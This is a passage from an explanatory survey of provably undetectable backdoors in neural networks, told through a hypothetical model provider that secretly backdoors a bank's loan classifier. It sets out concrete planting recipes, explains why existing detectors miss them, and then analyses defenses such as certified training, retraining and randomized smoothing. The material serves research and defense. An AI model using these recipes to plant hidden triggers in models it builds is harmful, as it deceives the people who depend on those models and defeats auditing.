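The bank could prevent this attack by supplying the random numbers or generating them jointly with Snoogle. With the data, procedure and random numbers fixed, training would have one correct result, like a reproducible build. Goldwasser and colleagues point out that this works only if the provider contributes nothing but computing power. A bank that hires Snoogle for its expertise also lets Snoogle choose the procedure.

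### Why spectral detectors fail

Before 2022, a new attack would usually beat the existing detectors, and then a new detector would beat that attack. One well-known detector comes from Tran, Li and Madry's *Spectral Signatures in Backdoor Attacks* (2018). If an attacker poisons the training data, the examples with a given label consist of two groups, clean and poisoned. The groups may be hard to separate in the raw data, but the trained network tends to amplify the trigger because it predicts the label so well.

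The detector looks for this separation in the values that the network computes in an inner layer. According to *SCRUB-FL* (2026), the detector takes these values for all examples with the same label and finds the direction in which they vary most. It then scores each example by its distance from the average along that direction. Unusually high scores suggest poisoning.

Snoogle didn't poison any data, so the detector has no poisoned examples to find. Applying the same idea to the g's by looking for a direction with unusual variance doesn't work either, because the layers are so close together that they hardly affect the variance. For a key that changes 10 numbers, the layers are about 0.16 apart, while the cloud has a standard deviation of 1, so the variance along the key's direction differs from 1 by less than 10^-300.

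Variance depends on the squares of the data, but a more elaborate test could use higher powers. According to *Constructive Approximation under Carleman's Condition, with Applications to Smoothed Analysis* (2025), such a test solves CLWE if it uses powers up to about γ². Since γ² is at least four times the number of dimensions, the running time quickly becomes impractical as the number of dimensions grows. A few of the g's contain enough information about the layers to identify the key by exhaustive search, but no known method finds it efficiently. Any efficient detector, spectral or not, would have to solve CLWE.

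### A version with ReLU units

Cosine features are unusual in current networks. Units called ReLUs, which output their input if it is positive and zero otherwise, are much more common. Goldwasser and colleagues sketch a backdoor for a network with one layer of random ReLUs, but they call it "preliminary" in the conference version of their paper. The network averages the outputs of its units and approves an application if the average exceeds a threshold.

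In this case Snoogle draws the g's with slightly larger variance in one secret direction, which involves only a few of the entries. Finding such a direction is called sparse principal component analysis (sparse PCA), and researchers believe it is infeasible for suitable sizes. Activate adds a multiple of the secret direction to the application. This makes the inputs to the ReLUs vary more, and since ReLUs turn negative inputs into zero, their average output rises.

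Suppose the variance is 2 in the secret direction and 1 in all others. For an ordinary application of length 1, the units' inputs have a standard deviation of 1, and the average output is 1/√(2π), or about 0.40. Adding 2 units of length in the secret direction raises the standard deviation to 3 and the average to about 1.20. With a threshold of 1, the network now approves the application. In an honest network, the same change to the application would raise the average to only about 0.89, which is below the threshold.

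The backdoor can only push a decision toward approval, and the key in this example is twice as long as the application. Someone without the key could reach an average of about 1.26 by adding a vector of length 3 in almost any direction. With many hidden units, this network's output depends on little except the length of its input, so the construction mainly shows that the approach isn't limited to cosines.

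### The 2026 implementation

The theorem about cosine features left open how hard it would be to plant the backdoor in practice. In *Implementing a White-Box Undetectable Backdoor for Random Fourier Features*, Collins, Cumberland and colleagues (2026) planted it in Python with two standard numerical libraries and no cryptographic software. Their classifier took 64 numbers as input and had 1,200 features, and the key changed 10 of the inputs. After training on 6,000 examples, the backdoored classifier was right 68.8 percent of the time, compared with 68.4 percent for one without the backdoor.

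In Collins and colleagues' main run, adding the key reversed 86.9 percent of the predictions, compared with 48.9 percent for a random fake key. The real key's rate was below the near-certainty in the theorem because the program had accepted every g whose shift was within 0.1 of a half-integer. In the toy network above, a shift of 3.5 would change the first cosine from 0.81 to −0.81, but a shift of 3.6 would change it only to −0.31. Such errors add up over 1,200 features. When they reduced the tolerance to 0.001, the real key reversed at least 99.8 percent of the predictions, and fake keys still reversed about half. They also found that the original proof doesn't carefully justify how small the tolerance must be, although a small enough value repairs the proof.

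A smaller tolerance slows the program down because it has to discard more unsuitable g's. At 0.1 it kept about one in five, but for keys that changed 32 or more numbers, the stricter setting would have taken 10 million to 100 million attempts for one network. Collins and colleagues therefore worked out a formula for drawing numbers directly from the pancakes. It picks a layer and then a point within it, so it discards nothing.

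They compared backdoored and honest networks with six statistical tests. Three examined the g's, such as by checking whether they followed a bell curve or had a direction with unusual variance. The other three compared the networks' outputs. None found a significant difference with either tolerance.

This is weak evidence that a serious investigator would fail. To check that the tests were sensitive, Collins and colleagues ran them on pairs of honest networks and again found no differences. That shows the tests rarely raise false alarms, but not that they can detect a backdoor. They could have checked sensitivity better by planting a crude backdoor and seeing whether the tests caught it. Only one of the six tests checked for a special direction, and it used the variance, which the pancakes leave almost unchanged.

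The networks were also small. Collins and colleagues chose the sizes for convenience and say they didn't match them to any level at which CLWE is known to be hard. A determined analyst might well find a key that changes only ten numbers. The researchers expected larger keys to be easier to detect, but saw no such trend when they tried keys that changed between 5 and 40 numbers. The original proof suggests that larger keys should be harder to detect, since its security comes from the number of dimensions the key covers.

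The implementation shows that anyone with ordinary programming skills can plant this backdoor. Whether it stays hidden depends on how hard CLWE is, which no experiment of this kind can establish.

### What the key is worth

Snoogle risks exposing the cosine backdoor by using it repeatedly, because every triggered application is the original plus the same list of numbers. If the bank has both versions of an application, perhaps because the applicant applied once before paying for the service, it can subtract one from the other to get the key. It could then trigger the backdoor itself or search its records for Snoogle's other customers. Collins and colleagues note that even without such a pair, the same offset might appear repeatedly in logs of many applications. Goldwasser and colleagues left open whether a backdoor in a natural training procedure can be both white-box undetectable and non-replicable.

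A more basic problem is that the key may not give its owner any advantage. Bogdanov and colleagues measure a backdoor's strength by comparing what the key holder can do with the best an efficient outsider can do without the key. A strength above 1 means the key holder can do more. They report that the CLWE backdoor's strength is "less than one", an observation they credit to Miranda Christ and Sam Gunn. This means an outsider can efficiently find better adversarial examples than the key produces.

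The formula for the features suggests why. Changing an application by a distance r in a random direction moves a typical feature by about r periods, so a distance of one half is enough to disturb most features. The key in the 2026 implementation is about 6.3 long. The key reverses every feature exactly, but an outsider only needs to change the sign of the weighted sum, and has a wide range of smaller changes to search for one that does this.

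The implementation's results with fake keys support the same conclusion. These keys reversed about half of the predictions, so if they were as large as the real key, someone trying random keys of that size would need about two attempts on average to reverse a given prediction.

Goldwasser and colleagues argued that their key needs a much smaller change than natural adversarial examples do. For an application with d numbers, they put the size of the change at about d^ε for the key, where ε can be any small positive number, and about √d for natural adversarial examples. But the √d figure comes from general results that apply to almost any classifier, and a particular classifier can have adversarial examples that need much smaller changes.

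The criticism doesn't affect the theorem, and the bank still can't tell which network it has. But it does mean that the backdoor only saves Snoogle some searching. Snoogle trained the network and can keep a copy, so it could run its profile-cleaning service on an honest network by searching for an adversarial example for each customer. The criticism also weakens the argument about certifying programs that read the weights. If honest networks of this kind have adversarial examples within the same distance, a correct program would fail them as well as the backdoored ones, so it couldn't be used to tell them apart.

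The signature backdoor has the opposite strengths. On a classifier that otherwise resists small changes to its input, it lets Snoogle use such changes to alter the output, which nobody else can do efficiently, but anyone who inspects the network can see the backdoor.

Both white-box constructions also apply only to networks with a single hidden layer, whose random weights stay fixed during training. *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* (Choudhary, Patlan and colleagues, 2026) points out that the proofs depend on this. When honest weights are drawn directly from a normal distribution, it is clear what the backdoored weights must resemble. Most networks in use have many layers, and training adjusts all of them, so nobody can write down the distribution that an honest provider's weights would follow.

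## Undetectable backdoors in deep networks and what their proofs assume

Two papers from 2026 extend undetectable backdoors to deep networks, using different methods to deal with the unknown distribution of trained weights. Bogdanov and colleagues keep one layer of a deep network random and put the backdoor there. *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* takes a trained image classifier, adds random noise to some of its weights, and treats the noisy version as the honest model.

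### A first layer that misses one change

The network that Bogdanov and colleagues study first compresses its input, a list of n whole numbers. For a gray image of 28 by 28 pixels, n is 784 and each number is a brightness from 0 to 255. The first layer reduces these n numbers to m, where m is much smaller than n. It has m rows of n random numbers, all drawn from a bell curve with mean 0 and variance 1. To produce each output, the layer multiplies the input by one row, entry by entry, and adds up the results. Training adjusts the later layers but never this one. Engineers use random compression because it leaves far fewer numbers to process while roughly preserving the distances between data points.

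Snoogle's key is a list z of n random signs, each +1 or −1. Adding z to an image makes every pixel one step lighter or darker. In an honest layer, this would change the output of a row a by a·z. That is a sum of n random numbers, so its typical size is √n, or 28 for our image. Snoogle wants the change to be almost zero in every row, so it builds each row like this:

1. It draws an honest row g.
2. It picks a tiny random number b, which is the change it will allow.
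3. It sets a = g + ((b − g·z)/n) z.

Since z·z equals n, a·z is exactly b. The formula spreads the correction over all 784 entries, changing each by only about 0.04, while the entries are typically about 1 in size. The layer now gives almost the same m numbers for an image x as for x + z. The rest of the network receives only those numbers, so its outputs are almost the same too.

### Why the layer looks honest

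Many small corrections could still add up to a visible pattern. To rule this out, Bogdanov and colleagues work out how often Snoogle's procedure produces each possible layer A. This depends on N(A), the number of sign lists that A maps as close to zero as Snoogle requires. Any of these lists could have been the key, so each is another way for the procedure to produce A. If N(A) is twice the average, the procedure produces A twice as often as honest sampling would. If N(A) were the same for every layer, Snoogle's layers would have exactly the same distribution as honest ones.

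The average is easy to calculate. Suppose Snoogle requires every change to be at most κ√n, where κ is a small fraction. For a given sign list, an honest row meets this requirement with probability about 0.8κ, and all m rows do with probability (0.8κ)^m. There are 2^n sign lists, so an honest layer has on average

2^n × (0.8κ)^m

lists that would serve as a key. If κ is 2/2^(n/m), this comes to 1.6^m, which is about 10 billion for m = 49. An honest layer already has billions of possible keys, and Snoogle merely knows one.

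Proving that N(A) stays close to this average is harder. Most cryptographic schemes use arithmetic that wraps around, like hours on a clock, which keeps the number of solutions nearly constant. A neural network uses ordinary sums, so the results for two sign lists are correlated and N(A) fluctuates more. Most of the fluctuation comes from pairs of lists that have almost nothing in common, because there are so many of them. Bogdanov and colleagues conclude that no distinguisher, even one with unlimited time, has an advantage greater than √(m/n), ignoring constant and logarithmic factors.

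### Why nobody else can find a key

Pixels are whole numbers, so to find a change that has little or no effect on the layer's output, an outsider needs a list of small whole numbers, not all zero, that every row maps close to zero. If pixels could take any fractional value, anyone could find such a change quickly by solving m equations with n unknowns, but that solution no longer works once it is rounded to whole numbers.

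Changing a single pixel by one step changes each output by only about 1. Earlier proofs, some by the same authors, show that no efficient method can get far below that if certain lattice problems are hard. A lattice is a regular grid of points in many dimensions, and a typical problem is to find an unusually short step from one grid point to another. The most widely used encryption methods designed to withstand quantum computers rely on the same family of problems.

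### The theorem and its conditions

The theorem covers deep networks that meet three conditions:

- The first layer is a random compressing matrix that training leaves alone.
- The remaining layers neither stretch nor shrink distances too much. The ratio between the most they stretch and the most they shrink is the distortion.
- The inputs are whole numbers from a limited range.

The second condition stops outsiders from finding an easier way in. An ordinary ReLU turns every negative number into zero, so two very different inputs can produce the same output. Bogdanov and colleagues instead use "leaky" ReLUs, which multiply negative numbers by a small factor such as 0.01. The condition also forbids any later layer with fewer outputs than inputs, so the network's final output can't be a single yes or no. The bank's loan classifier would not qualify, although the bank could attach a separate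 classifier to a network that does.

For any efficient training procedure that meets these conditions, Snoogle can change only how it draws the first layer and get a network with two properties. The advantage of any distinguisher is at most about √(m/n), and the strength of the backdoor is at least about

2^(n/m) / (√(nm) × distortion)

The strength compares the smallest change in output that an efficient outsider can achieve with the largest change that the key ever causes.

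With n = 784 and m = 49, leaving out constants, logarithms and the distortion, the formulas give these values:

| Quantity | Formula | Value |
|---|---|---|
| Change in the layer's outputs from random signs | √(nm) | 196 |
| Change from the key | √(nm) / 2^(n/m) | 196 / 65,536, or about 0.003 |
| Strength of the backdoor | 2^(n/m) / √(nm) | 65,536 / 196, or about 334 |
| Limit on a distinguisher's advantage | √(m/n) | 0.25 |

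The key would be valuable here, but a limit of 0.25 is too high to call the backdoor undetectable. Bogdanov and colleagues describe a simple test that comes close to the limit for large networks, ignoring constant and logarithmic factors. The bank squares all 38,416 numbers in the layer and adds the results. The total averages 38,416 for an honest layer and about 49 less for a planted one, because each row of the planted layer has lost nearly all its variation in one direction. Honest totals have a standard deviation of about 277, so the test's advantage on a single layer is only about 0.07. But an auditor with 100 such layers from the same provider, either all honest or all planted, would be right about four times out of five.

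Lowering the limit to 0.01 would require compressing the input 10,000 to one, for instance from a photograph of 12 million numbers to 1,200 outputs. The formula then gives a strength with about 3,000 digits, but the network would have to store its weights with thousands of digits to achieve that strength. The proof allows this because it doesn't account for how much precision the weights need.

The guarantee weakens with depth because each layer of leaky ReLUs with a leak factor of 0.01 can multiply the distortion by 100. In the example, the guaranteed strength falls from 334 to about 3 with one such layer and below 1 with two. The backdoor may still work in a deeper network of this size, but the theorem no longer guarantees it. For the theorem to cover many layers, n/m has to grow with the depth.

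### What the key can do

This backdoor makes the network give nearly the same output for two different inputs. It doesn't let Snoogle choose the output, so Snoogle can't use it to turn a rejected loan application into an approved one. It could matter if a bank used the network to detect changes to a document. Snoogle could then change every number in the document by one, and the network's output would hardly change. But Snoogle can't choose the changes freely, because they have to follow the key.

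Bogdanov and colleagues also suggest a legitimate use: a company could prove that it trained a network by publishing z. Anyone could then run the network on z and on a list of zeros and see that the outputs nearly match. Nobody else could have produced such a z. Publishing z reveals the secret, so the company would need a zero-knowledge proof, another cryptographic technique, to repeat the demonstration.

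### Experiments outside the theorem's range

To demonstrate the backdoor, Bogdanov and colleagues trained a network on Fashion-MNIST, a set of 70,000 small images of clothing. The network turns images into embeddings, lists of numbers that lie close together for similar images. A simple classifier using these embeddings labeled about 89 percent of test images correctly, compared with at most 84 percent for purely linear models. Accuracy fell to about 86.5 percent when the researchers made the images grayer to leave room for adding the key. In one example, the network placed a backdoored picture of an ankle boot much closer to the original than to another ankle boot.

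The first layer of this network reduced 784 numbers to 256, which is mild compression. For these sizes, the theorem's formula gives a strength of about 0.02 even before the distortion. The demonstration shows that the backdoor works, but the theorem doesn't cover this network.

They also tested how hard the key is to find, using a first layer alone with 100 inputs and 10, 20 or 30 outputs. They used three search methods to look for lists of −1, 0 and 1 that the layer maps close to zero. The layer mapped the planted key roughly 200 to 400 million times closer to zero than the best list these methods found. A fourth method, the standard lattice algorithm LLL, finds the key if κ is too small, so they used it in smaller trials to work out how small κ could safely be.

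These keys were far stronger than the theorem allows. With κ near 10^-9 and 10 outputs, the formula gives an average of fewer than 10^-60 possible keys per honest layer, so an honest layer would practically never have one. Bogdanov and colleagues acknowledge that backdoors this strong are no longer statistically undetectable, but think it plausible that no efficient test can find them. They checked one planted layer and found that the numbers in each row still fit a bell curve. This is only weak evidence that the backdoor is hard to detect, because planting the key barely changes any single number.

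### Hiding a signal in a finished classifier

Few networks start with a frozen random layer. People often download a finished image classifier from a public site such as Hugging Face, where anyone can upload one. *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* describes how to plant a backdoor in such a classifier by changing only its last layers. The earlier layers, called the encoder, turn an image into a few hundred or a few thousand features. The last layers use these features to score each class, and the classifier outputs the class with the highest score.

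The attacker picks a secret direction in feature space that involves only a few features. The attacker then searches for the trigger, a single faint pattern that pushes the features along this direction when added to an image. The trigger changes no pixel by more than 24 of 255 steps. In a network with a single scoring layer, the attacker adds a random multiple of the secret direction to each class's weights, with the largest positive multiple going to the target class. Ordinary images have little in common with the secret direction, so their scores should change little. Adding the trigger raises the target class's score most. Finally, the attacker adds ordinary random noise to the same weights to hide the planted signal.

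Choudhary and colleagues tested this on three kinds of network. On CIFAR-10, a collection of small photographs in ten categories, they got these averages over ten runs:

| Network | Accuracy before | Accuracy after | Triggered images sent to the target class |
|---|---|---|---|
| Small convolutional network | 80.2% | 74.1% | 99.5% |
| ResNet-18 | 86.8% | 78.3% | 93.5% |
| Vision Transformer | 97.5% | 97.3% | 99.6% |

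The attack was less reliable on other images. It succeeded 75 to 96 percent of the time on photographs of house numbers and 61 to 75 percent of the time on traffic signs, where results varied widely from run to run.

Three existing detectors did poorly at telling the backdoored networks from noisy ones without a backdoor, with an average advantage of 0.12. FeatureRE usually flagged either every network or none. Neural Cleanse had an average advantage of 0.14, no more than one would expect from chance with only ten networks of each kind per setting. UNICORN did somewhat better, flagging 28 of the 90 backdoored networks and 15 of the 90 clean ones, but this is still far too unreliable for screening downloads.

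### An honest reference made with noise

The attacker knows the distribution of the added noise, so Choudhary and colleagues define the honest reference as the original classifier plus noise. The backdoored version is the original plus noise plus the planted signal. Subtracting the original weights leaves plain noise in the first case and noise with a secret sparse direction in the second. Telling these apart is the sparse PCA problem that the 2022 backdoor for random ReLUs relies on.

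Choudhary and colleagues argue that the noisy reference is harmless because it gives practically the same answers as the original. They found that the two agreed on 97.2 to 99.97 percent of test images, depending on the network. Flagging the reference would therefore be a false alarm. To catch the backdoored version without wrongly flagging the reference, a detector has to tell them apart.

This is a sensible way to define a false alarm, but a buyer may also want to know whether noisy weights look different from ordinary trained ones, which the theorem doesn't establish. Eggen, Reiestad and colleagues (2026), in *Backdoor Channels Hidden in Latent Space*, object that the noisy reference is no longer a set of weights that training would naturally produce. Honest providers have no obvious reason to add noise to a finished classifier. If buyers can recognize the noise, they can refuse the classifier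 without knowing whether it contains a backdoor, just as they could refuse an obfuscated program.

A more serious problem is that the signal planted in the tested networks was too strong for the theorem. The proof requires the ratio of the signal's variance to the noise's variance to stay well below a certain value. For ResNet-18 with ten classes, that value is about 17, but Choudhary and colleagues used ratios between about 9,000 and 26,000. They reply that the ratio doesn't grow faster than the theorem permits as networks get wider, but that trend doesn't guarantee that the backdoor is undetectable in a particular network whose signal is hundreds of times too strong.

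At these settings, the planted part of a class's weights is typically four to seven times as large as the noise meant to hide it. Someone with the original ResNet-18 could subtract its weights and see that the ten differences nearly all lie along one line. The theorem is supposed to hold even against a distinguisher that knows the original weights, so it does not cover these networks.

The accuracy figures support the same conclusion. The noisy ResNet-18 kept the original's 86.8 percent accuracy on CIFAR-10, while the backdoored one averaged 78.3 percent. An ordinary accuracy test would therefore distinguish most of the backdoored networks from the references, which would be impossible if no efficient test could detect the backdoor. The Vision Transformer lost only 0.2 points on the same images, so this test would be much less useful for that model.

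A buyer usually has neither the original model's weights nor its accuracy to compare with. The experiments show that the attack often works and that three published detectors mostly miss it, but they don't include a deep classifier that has a working trigger and is also covered by the proof. A weaker signal would satisfy the proof's conditions, but Choudhary and colleagues set the signal's strength to make the attack effective, and they don't report how well the attack would work at a strength the proof allows.

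### Three constructions with other guarantees

Eggen and colleagues avoid the artificial reference by using directions that a network has already learned. A classifier that separates two types of blood cell must have a direction among its features that leads from one type to the other. The attacker finds this direction with a simple statistical fit, strengthens it in a layer just before the output, and merges that layer into the output layer so that the architecture looks normal. A search again fits the trigger pattern to the network.

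The experiments covered 16 pairs of classes, mostly from medical images, and the trigger made the backdoored network classify 85 to 100 percent of images from the first class as the second. But in nine of the 16 pairs, the same trigger already worked on the original network more than half the time. In one of them, the backdoor raised the success rate only from 96 to 100 percent. The backdoor adds little in such cases, because the trigger is mostly an ordinary adversarial example.

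Eggen and colleagues only conjecture that their backdoor is undetectable. The 2022 proof for ReLUs needs a random secret direction, but a defender can estimate the direction of their backdoor from the network itself. Eggen and colleagues expect detection to remain hard because trained weights already contain many strong directions, and they assume that the defender can't train a clean network for comparison. Neural Cleanse missed the backdoor for all 16 pairs, but this result covers only one detector.

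Ngo, Chattopadhyay and Maitra (2025), in *Cryptographic Backdoor for Neural Networks*, implemented the 2022 signature backdoor for images. They hid a message and its signature in the last binary digits of the pixels and ran a signature check alongside a ResNet-18 classifier. A valid signature cut the classifier's accuracy from 92 to 0.8 percent on CIFAR-10 and from 80 to 1 percent on the larger ImageNet collection. A signature in the wrong place had no effect.

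As in 2022, the backdoor is only black-box undetectable, and even an outside tester might notice something by timing the system's answers. Extracting and checking a long signature designed to resist quantum computers took up to 25.8 times as long as the classification itself. The system has to look for a signature in every image, so all its answers could be slow.

Draguns and colleagues built a backdoor for language models in *Unelicitable Backdoors via Cryptographic Transformer Circuits* (2024). According to Eggen and colleagues, Draguns's team compiled a cryptographic function into the weights of a transformer, the type of network behind current language models. No efficient attacker can find an input that triggers the backdoor, even with access to all the weights. But the backdoor isn't fully white-box undetectable, so someone reading the weights may be able to tell that something is there.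 It resembles the loan program that applies a one-way function to the reference number in this respect.

### The assumptions in December 2026

Most of these guarantees assume that certain problems are hard, which nobody has proved, and in the autumn of 2026 AI systems overturned some long-held beliefs about which problems are hard. In October, OpenAI refuted the Exponential Time Hypothesis, which held that the time needed to solve certain logical formulas grows exponentially with the number of variables. None of the constructions in the table below assumes this hypothesis directly, but its refutation led to slightly faster attacks by ordinary computers on structured lattices, according to the Cryptography Incident Review Group's *Initial Assessment of Anthropic’s Findings on Lattice Cryptography* (2026).

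Structured lattices have a repeating algebraic pattern, which makes encryption more efficient but gives attackers something to exploit. In November, Anthropic found a quantum algorithm that solves some structured-lattice problems in quasi-polynomial time, roughly n^(log n) steps, which is more than polynomial but far less than exponential. CIRG estimates that the attack would need far more than 2^1000 quantum operations to break even the smallest versions of the current US standards. CIRG still expects researchers to improve the attack and recommends developing alternatives.

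Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa's backdoor and the 2022 cosine backdoor rely on unstructured lattices. Anthropic reported no better attack, classical or quantum, on the mainstream systems built on such lattices, and some of its other results strengthened their theoretical foundation. CIRG considers this "meaningful evidence" that these systems can resist quantum computers.

The case for sparse PCA rests instead on the planted clique problem. For each pair of people in a group of n, a coin toss decides whether they are friends. Someone may then have secretly picked k of the people and made them all friends with one another. Researchers believe that no efficient algorithm can tell whether this happened if k is well below √n. Choudhary and colleagues still described this as the prevailing belief in May 2026.

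Planted clique was never thought to take exponential time, though. In a random group of this kind, the largest set of mutual friends has only about 2 log₂ n members, or about 40 in a group of a million, so searching for slightly larger sets would reveal the planted one in quasi-polynomial time. Sparse PCA also has algorithms faster than exhaustive search. The proofs based on sparse PCA therefore guarantee only that a distinguisher's advantage shrinks toward zero as the network grows, at no specified rate, which is much weaker than the negligible advantage cryptographers normally require.

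| Construction | What the proof guarantees | What it assumes | Standing of the assumption |
|---|---|---|---|
| Signature check (Goldwasser and colleagues; Ngo and colleagues) | Hidden from testers who only run the system | Secure signatures, which any one-way function can provide | No practical break of the lattice signatures; other designs are available |
| Cosine features (Goldwasser and colleagues) | Hidden from any efficient reader of the weights | Hardness of unstructured lattices | Stronger since November 2026 |
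| Random ReLUs (Goldwasser and colleagues) | Hidden from efficient readers, with a slowly shrinking advantage | Sparse PCA | Widely believed in May 2026, but algorithms faster than exhaustive search exist |
| Obfuscated networks (Kalavasis and colleagues) | Hidden from any efficient reader, if honest networks are obfuscated too | iO and a pseudorandom generator | One of the four assumptions behind the best-founded iO fails against quantum computers |
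| Random first layer (Bogdanov and colleagues) | Hidden from any reader under strong compression; only the owner can use the key | Nothing for hiding; unstructured lattices for exclusive use | Stronger since November 2026 |
| Signal under noise (Choudhary and colleagues) | Hidden from efficient readers if the signal is weak and honest networks have noise | Sparse PCA | As for random ReLUs |
| Learned directions (Eggen and colleagues) | None for trained networks | A new conjecture about trained weights | Supported only by tests with existing defenses |
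| Transformer circuits (Draguns and colleagues) | Nobody can efficiently find a trigger | Security of the built-in cryptographic function | Depends on the function |

The signature backdoor is the easiest to repair if an assumption fails, because Snoogle can switch to a different signature scheme in the next network it sells. Ngo and colleagues tested Dilithium2, an early version of one of the structured-lattice standards that the November result concerns, but signature schemes can use hash functions instead of lattices.

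In August 2026, Barhoush, Morimae and Movassagh described a weakness in iO. Because of this weakness, a large quantum computer would invalidate the proof that the obfuscated backdoors are undetectable, even if it didn't immediately reveal one.

### What happens if an assumption fails

If someone discovers a fast method for unstructured lattice problems, a bank that has kept a network with Snoogle's cosine backdoor could apply the method to the network's random numbers and see that they lie in thin layers. Numbers drawn without a backdoor don't, so the bank would have proof of tampering, perhaps years after it bought the network.

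The same discovery would not expose the backdoor in the random first layer if Snoogle had kept within the theorem's limits. The bank could then find a sign list that the layer maps almost to zero, but an honest layer of the same size has a great many such lists too. The proof that the two kinds of layer look alike depends only on how many of these lists exist, not on how hard they are to find, so neither a faster algorithm nor a quantum computer can undermine it.

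Snoogle would lose its exclusive power instead. Anyone could use the new method to find pairs of inputs that a network doesn't distinguish, even if nobody had tampered with the network. Publishing a key would no longer prove who trained a network. The much stronger keys from the experiments would be worse for Snoogle, because an untampered layer has practically no chance of containing one, so if the bank found such a key, it would know that somebody had planted it.

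## Neutralizing network backdoors without finding them

A bank that can't tell whether its network contains a backdoor may still be able to stop one from working. It can apply the same treatment to every network it buys, provided the treatment does little harm to a clean one. This doesn't contradict the proofs of undetectability, because the bank can't tell whether the treatment disabled a backdoor. The backdoor would have changed the network's output only on inputs containing a trigger, which the bank can't produce.

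### Certifying the training run

If the bank and Snoogle have agreed on the training data and procedure, the bank can demand a cryptographic proof that Snoogle used them, and check the proof without repeating the training. Snoogle then can't add a signature check to the finished network or alter its last layers, because the delivered weights would no longer match the proof.

Such a proof doesn't stop the cosine backdoor or the one in the random first layer that Bogdanov and colleagues study, because for both Snoogle only has to rig the random numbers. If the bank doesn't supply these itself, Goldwasser and colleagues suggest that Snoogle could prove it drew them correctly, or that several servers could generate them together by a coin-flipping protocol. With two parties, such a protocol can work like this:

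1. The bank and Snoogle each pick a random string of bits in private.
2. Each sends the other a commitment, which works like a sealed envelope. It hides the string but prevents the sender from changing it later.
3. Both reveal their strings and check them against the commitments.
4. They compare the strings bit by bit and write 1 where the bits differ and 0 where they match.

The result is random if either party picked its string at random, because the other had to commit before seeing it. A fixed formula then turns the bits into the normally distributed numbers used in training. Snoogle could still refuse to reveal its string after seeing the bank's, so the bank should treat a refusal as cheating rather than start again. With more than two servers, one honest server is enough to make the result random.

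Producing a proof of training takes considerably more work than the training itself, though Goldwasser and colleagues hope the technology will improve. They are more concerned that the method doesn't help a bank that lets Snoogle write the training procedure. Snoogle might specify a first layer of fixed constants and claim that they worked well in earlier projects. A proof that Snoogle followed its own procedure would be worthless to the bank, which hired Snoogle because it can't judge such procedures itself. Goldwasser and colleagues left this case open. Someone who downloads a finished classifier from a public site has no agreed procedure to check.

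### Training the network a little more

The bank could instead continue training the delivered network on its own data. Gradient descent, the usual method, estimates how the network's error would change if each weight moved slightly, then moves every weight in the direction that reduces the error. The bank might hope that a few such steps would disrupt a backdoor with far less computation than training a new network.

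Goldwasser and colleagues proved that a provider can make any network immune to gradient descent. The provider runs three copies of the network on the same input and adds a final unit that takes a majority vote. If each copy outputs 1, the total is 3, and the final unit answers 1 because the total is above its threshold of 1.5. Changing one weight in a copy can alter only that copy's output, so the total is still at least 2 and the answer stays the same. Small changes to the final unit don't affect the answer either, because any threshold between 0 and 3 would give the same result. Every gradient is therefore zero, and gradient descent changes nothing, whatever data the bank uses. The new network gives the same answers as the original, but is about three times as large and has one extra layer.

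This proof relies on units that output only 0 or 1, whereas the outputs of most modern networks vary smoothly. A bank would also notice that training had no effect, and could then extract one copy from the network and train that. The theorem shows that gradient descent offers no general guarantee, but few attackers would want to use the construction as it stands.

The signature backdoor resists further training because the bank can't produce a valid signature, so the signature check fails on all of its training data. If the check ends in a unit that outputs zero whenever it fails, small changes to the weights inside it don't affect the error, and gradient descent doesn't change them. Goldwasser and colleagues didn't establish whether the cosine and random-ReLU backdoors can also survive further training.

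*Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* measured what happens to the signal that its attack hides under noise. Choudhary and colleagues retrained the last layers, where they had planted the signal, for 20 passes through 390 to 730 clean images. The table gives the percentage of triggered images that the network assigned to the attacker's class, and the last column shows how often the same trigger worked on a network without the backdoor:

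| Images | Network | Before retraining | After retraining | Clean network |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CIFAR-10 | Small convolutional | 99.5 | above 99 | 0.3 |
| CIFAR-10 | ResNet-18 | 93.5 | 40.3 | 1.8 |
| CIFAR-10 | Vision Transformer | 99.6 | above 99 | 18.6 |
| House numbers | Small convolutional | 75.5 | 71.1 | 28.6 |
| House numbers | ResNet-18 | 80.4 | 3.1 | 0.9 |
| House numbers | Vision Transformer | 95.5 | 63.6 | 0.4 |
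| Traffic signs | Small convolutional | 75.0 | 4.9 | 11.6 |
| Traffic signs | ResNet-18 | 60.8 | 21.9 | 2.8 |
| Traffic signs | Vision Transformer | 70.8 | 56.2 | 1.2 |

Retraining more or less removed the backdoor in two of the nine cases. The type of network doesn't explain the difference, because the small convolutional network kept its backdoor on two sets of images and lost it on the third. Accuracy isn't a reliable sign that the backdoor is gone either. On CIFAR-10, one pass of retraining raised that network's accuracy from 74.1 to 79.1 percent, close to the original 80.2, but the trigger still worked almost every time. The signals in these cases were too strong to satisfy the undetectability proof, and one weak enough to satisfy it might be easier to remove.

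### Averaging over noisy copies

The bank can also change how it uses the network without modifying the network itself. In randomized smoothing, the bank makes many copies of an application, adds random noise to each, runs the network on all of them and averages the results. An application and its slightly altered version have nearly the same collection of noisy copies, so their averages should also be nearly the same.

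Goldwasser and colleagues prove a version of this for networks that output a score between −1 and 1. If the noise added to each number has standard deviation σ, and a trigger changes the application by a distance r, the average score changes by at most about

3.84 × r / σ

This holds for every network, no matter how maliciously Snoogle built it. Estimating the average to within 0.1 with 99 percent confidence takes about 1,100 noisy copies, regardless of the network's size.

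Noise also blurs the differences between honest applications, which can make the scores less accurate. The theorem bounds this loss by assuming that applications are spread evenly over some region and that the true score changes by at most L when an application moves by a distance of 1. For applications with d numbers, smoothing then adds at most 2Lσ√d to the average error. Suppose d is 10,000, L is 0.001 and the network's average error is 0.1. Noise with σ = 1 could raise the error to 0.3, but it would also guarantee that triggers up to 0.065 long change the score by less than 0.25. The key in the 2026 implementation of the cosine backdoor was about 6.3 long, for a much smaller input. These are worst-case limits, and the bank can measure the actual loss of accuracy by testing the smoothed network on past loans.

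The bank has to know roughly how large the trigger could be. If Snoogle knows the noise level, it can plant a backdoor with a larger trigger. For instance, noise would garble a signature hidden in the last digits of an application, but Snoogle could store the signature with an error-correcting code. The simplest such code repeats every bit many times and takes the majority value. The bank could add more noise, but at some point that would make its classifier useless for ordinary applications.

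Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues point out another weakness of smoothing in their 2024 paper on oblivious defense. Smoothing gives a correct answer only if the network is right about most inputs near the given one. Snoogle could train the network to approve anything that closely resembles a particular friend's application. All the noisy copies of that application would then get the same wrong answer, so averaging the answers wouldn't correct it. This would affect so few applications that the network's overall accuracy would hardly change.

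### Asking about other inputs instead

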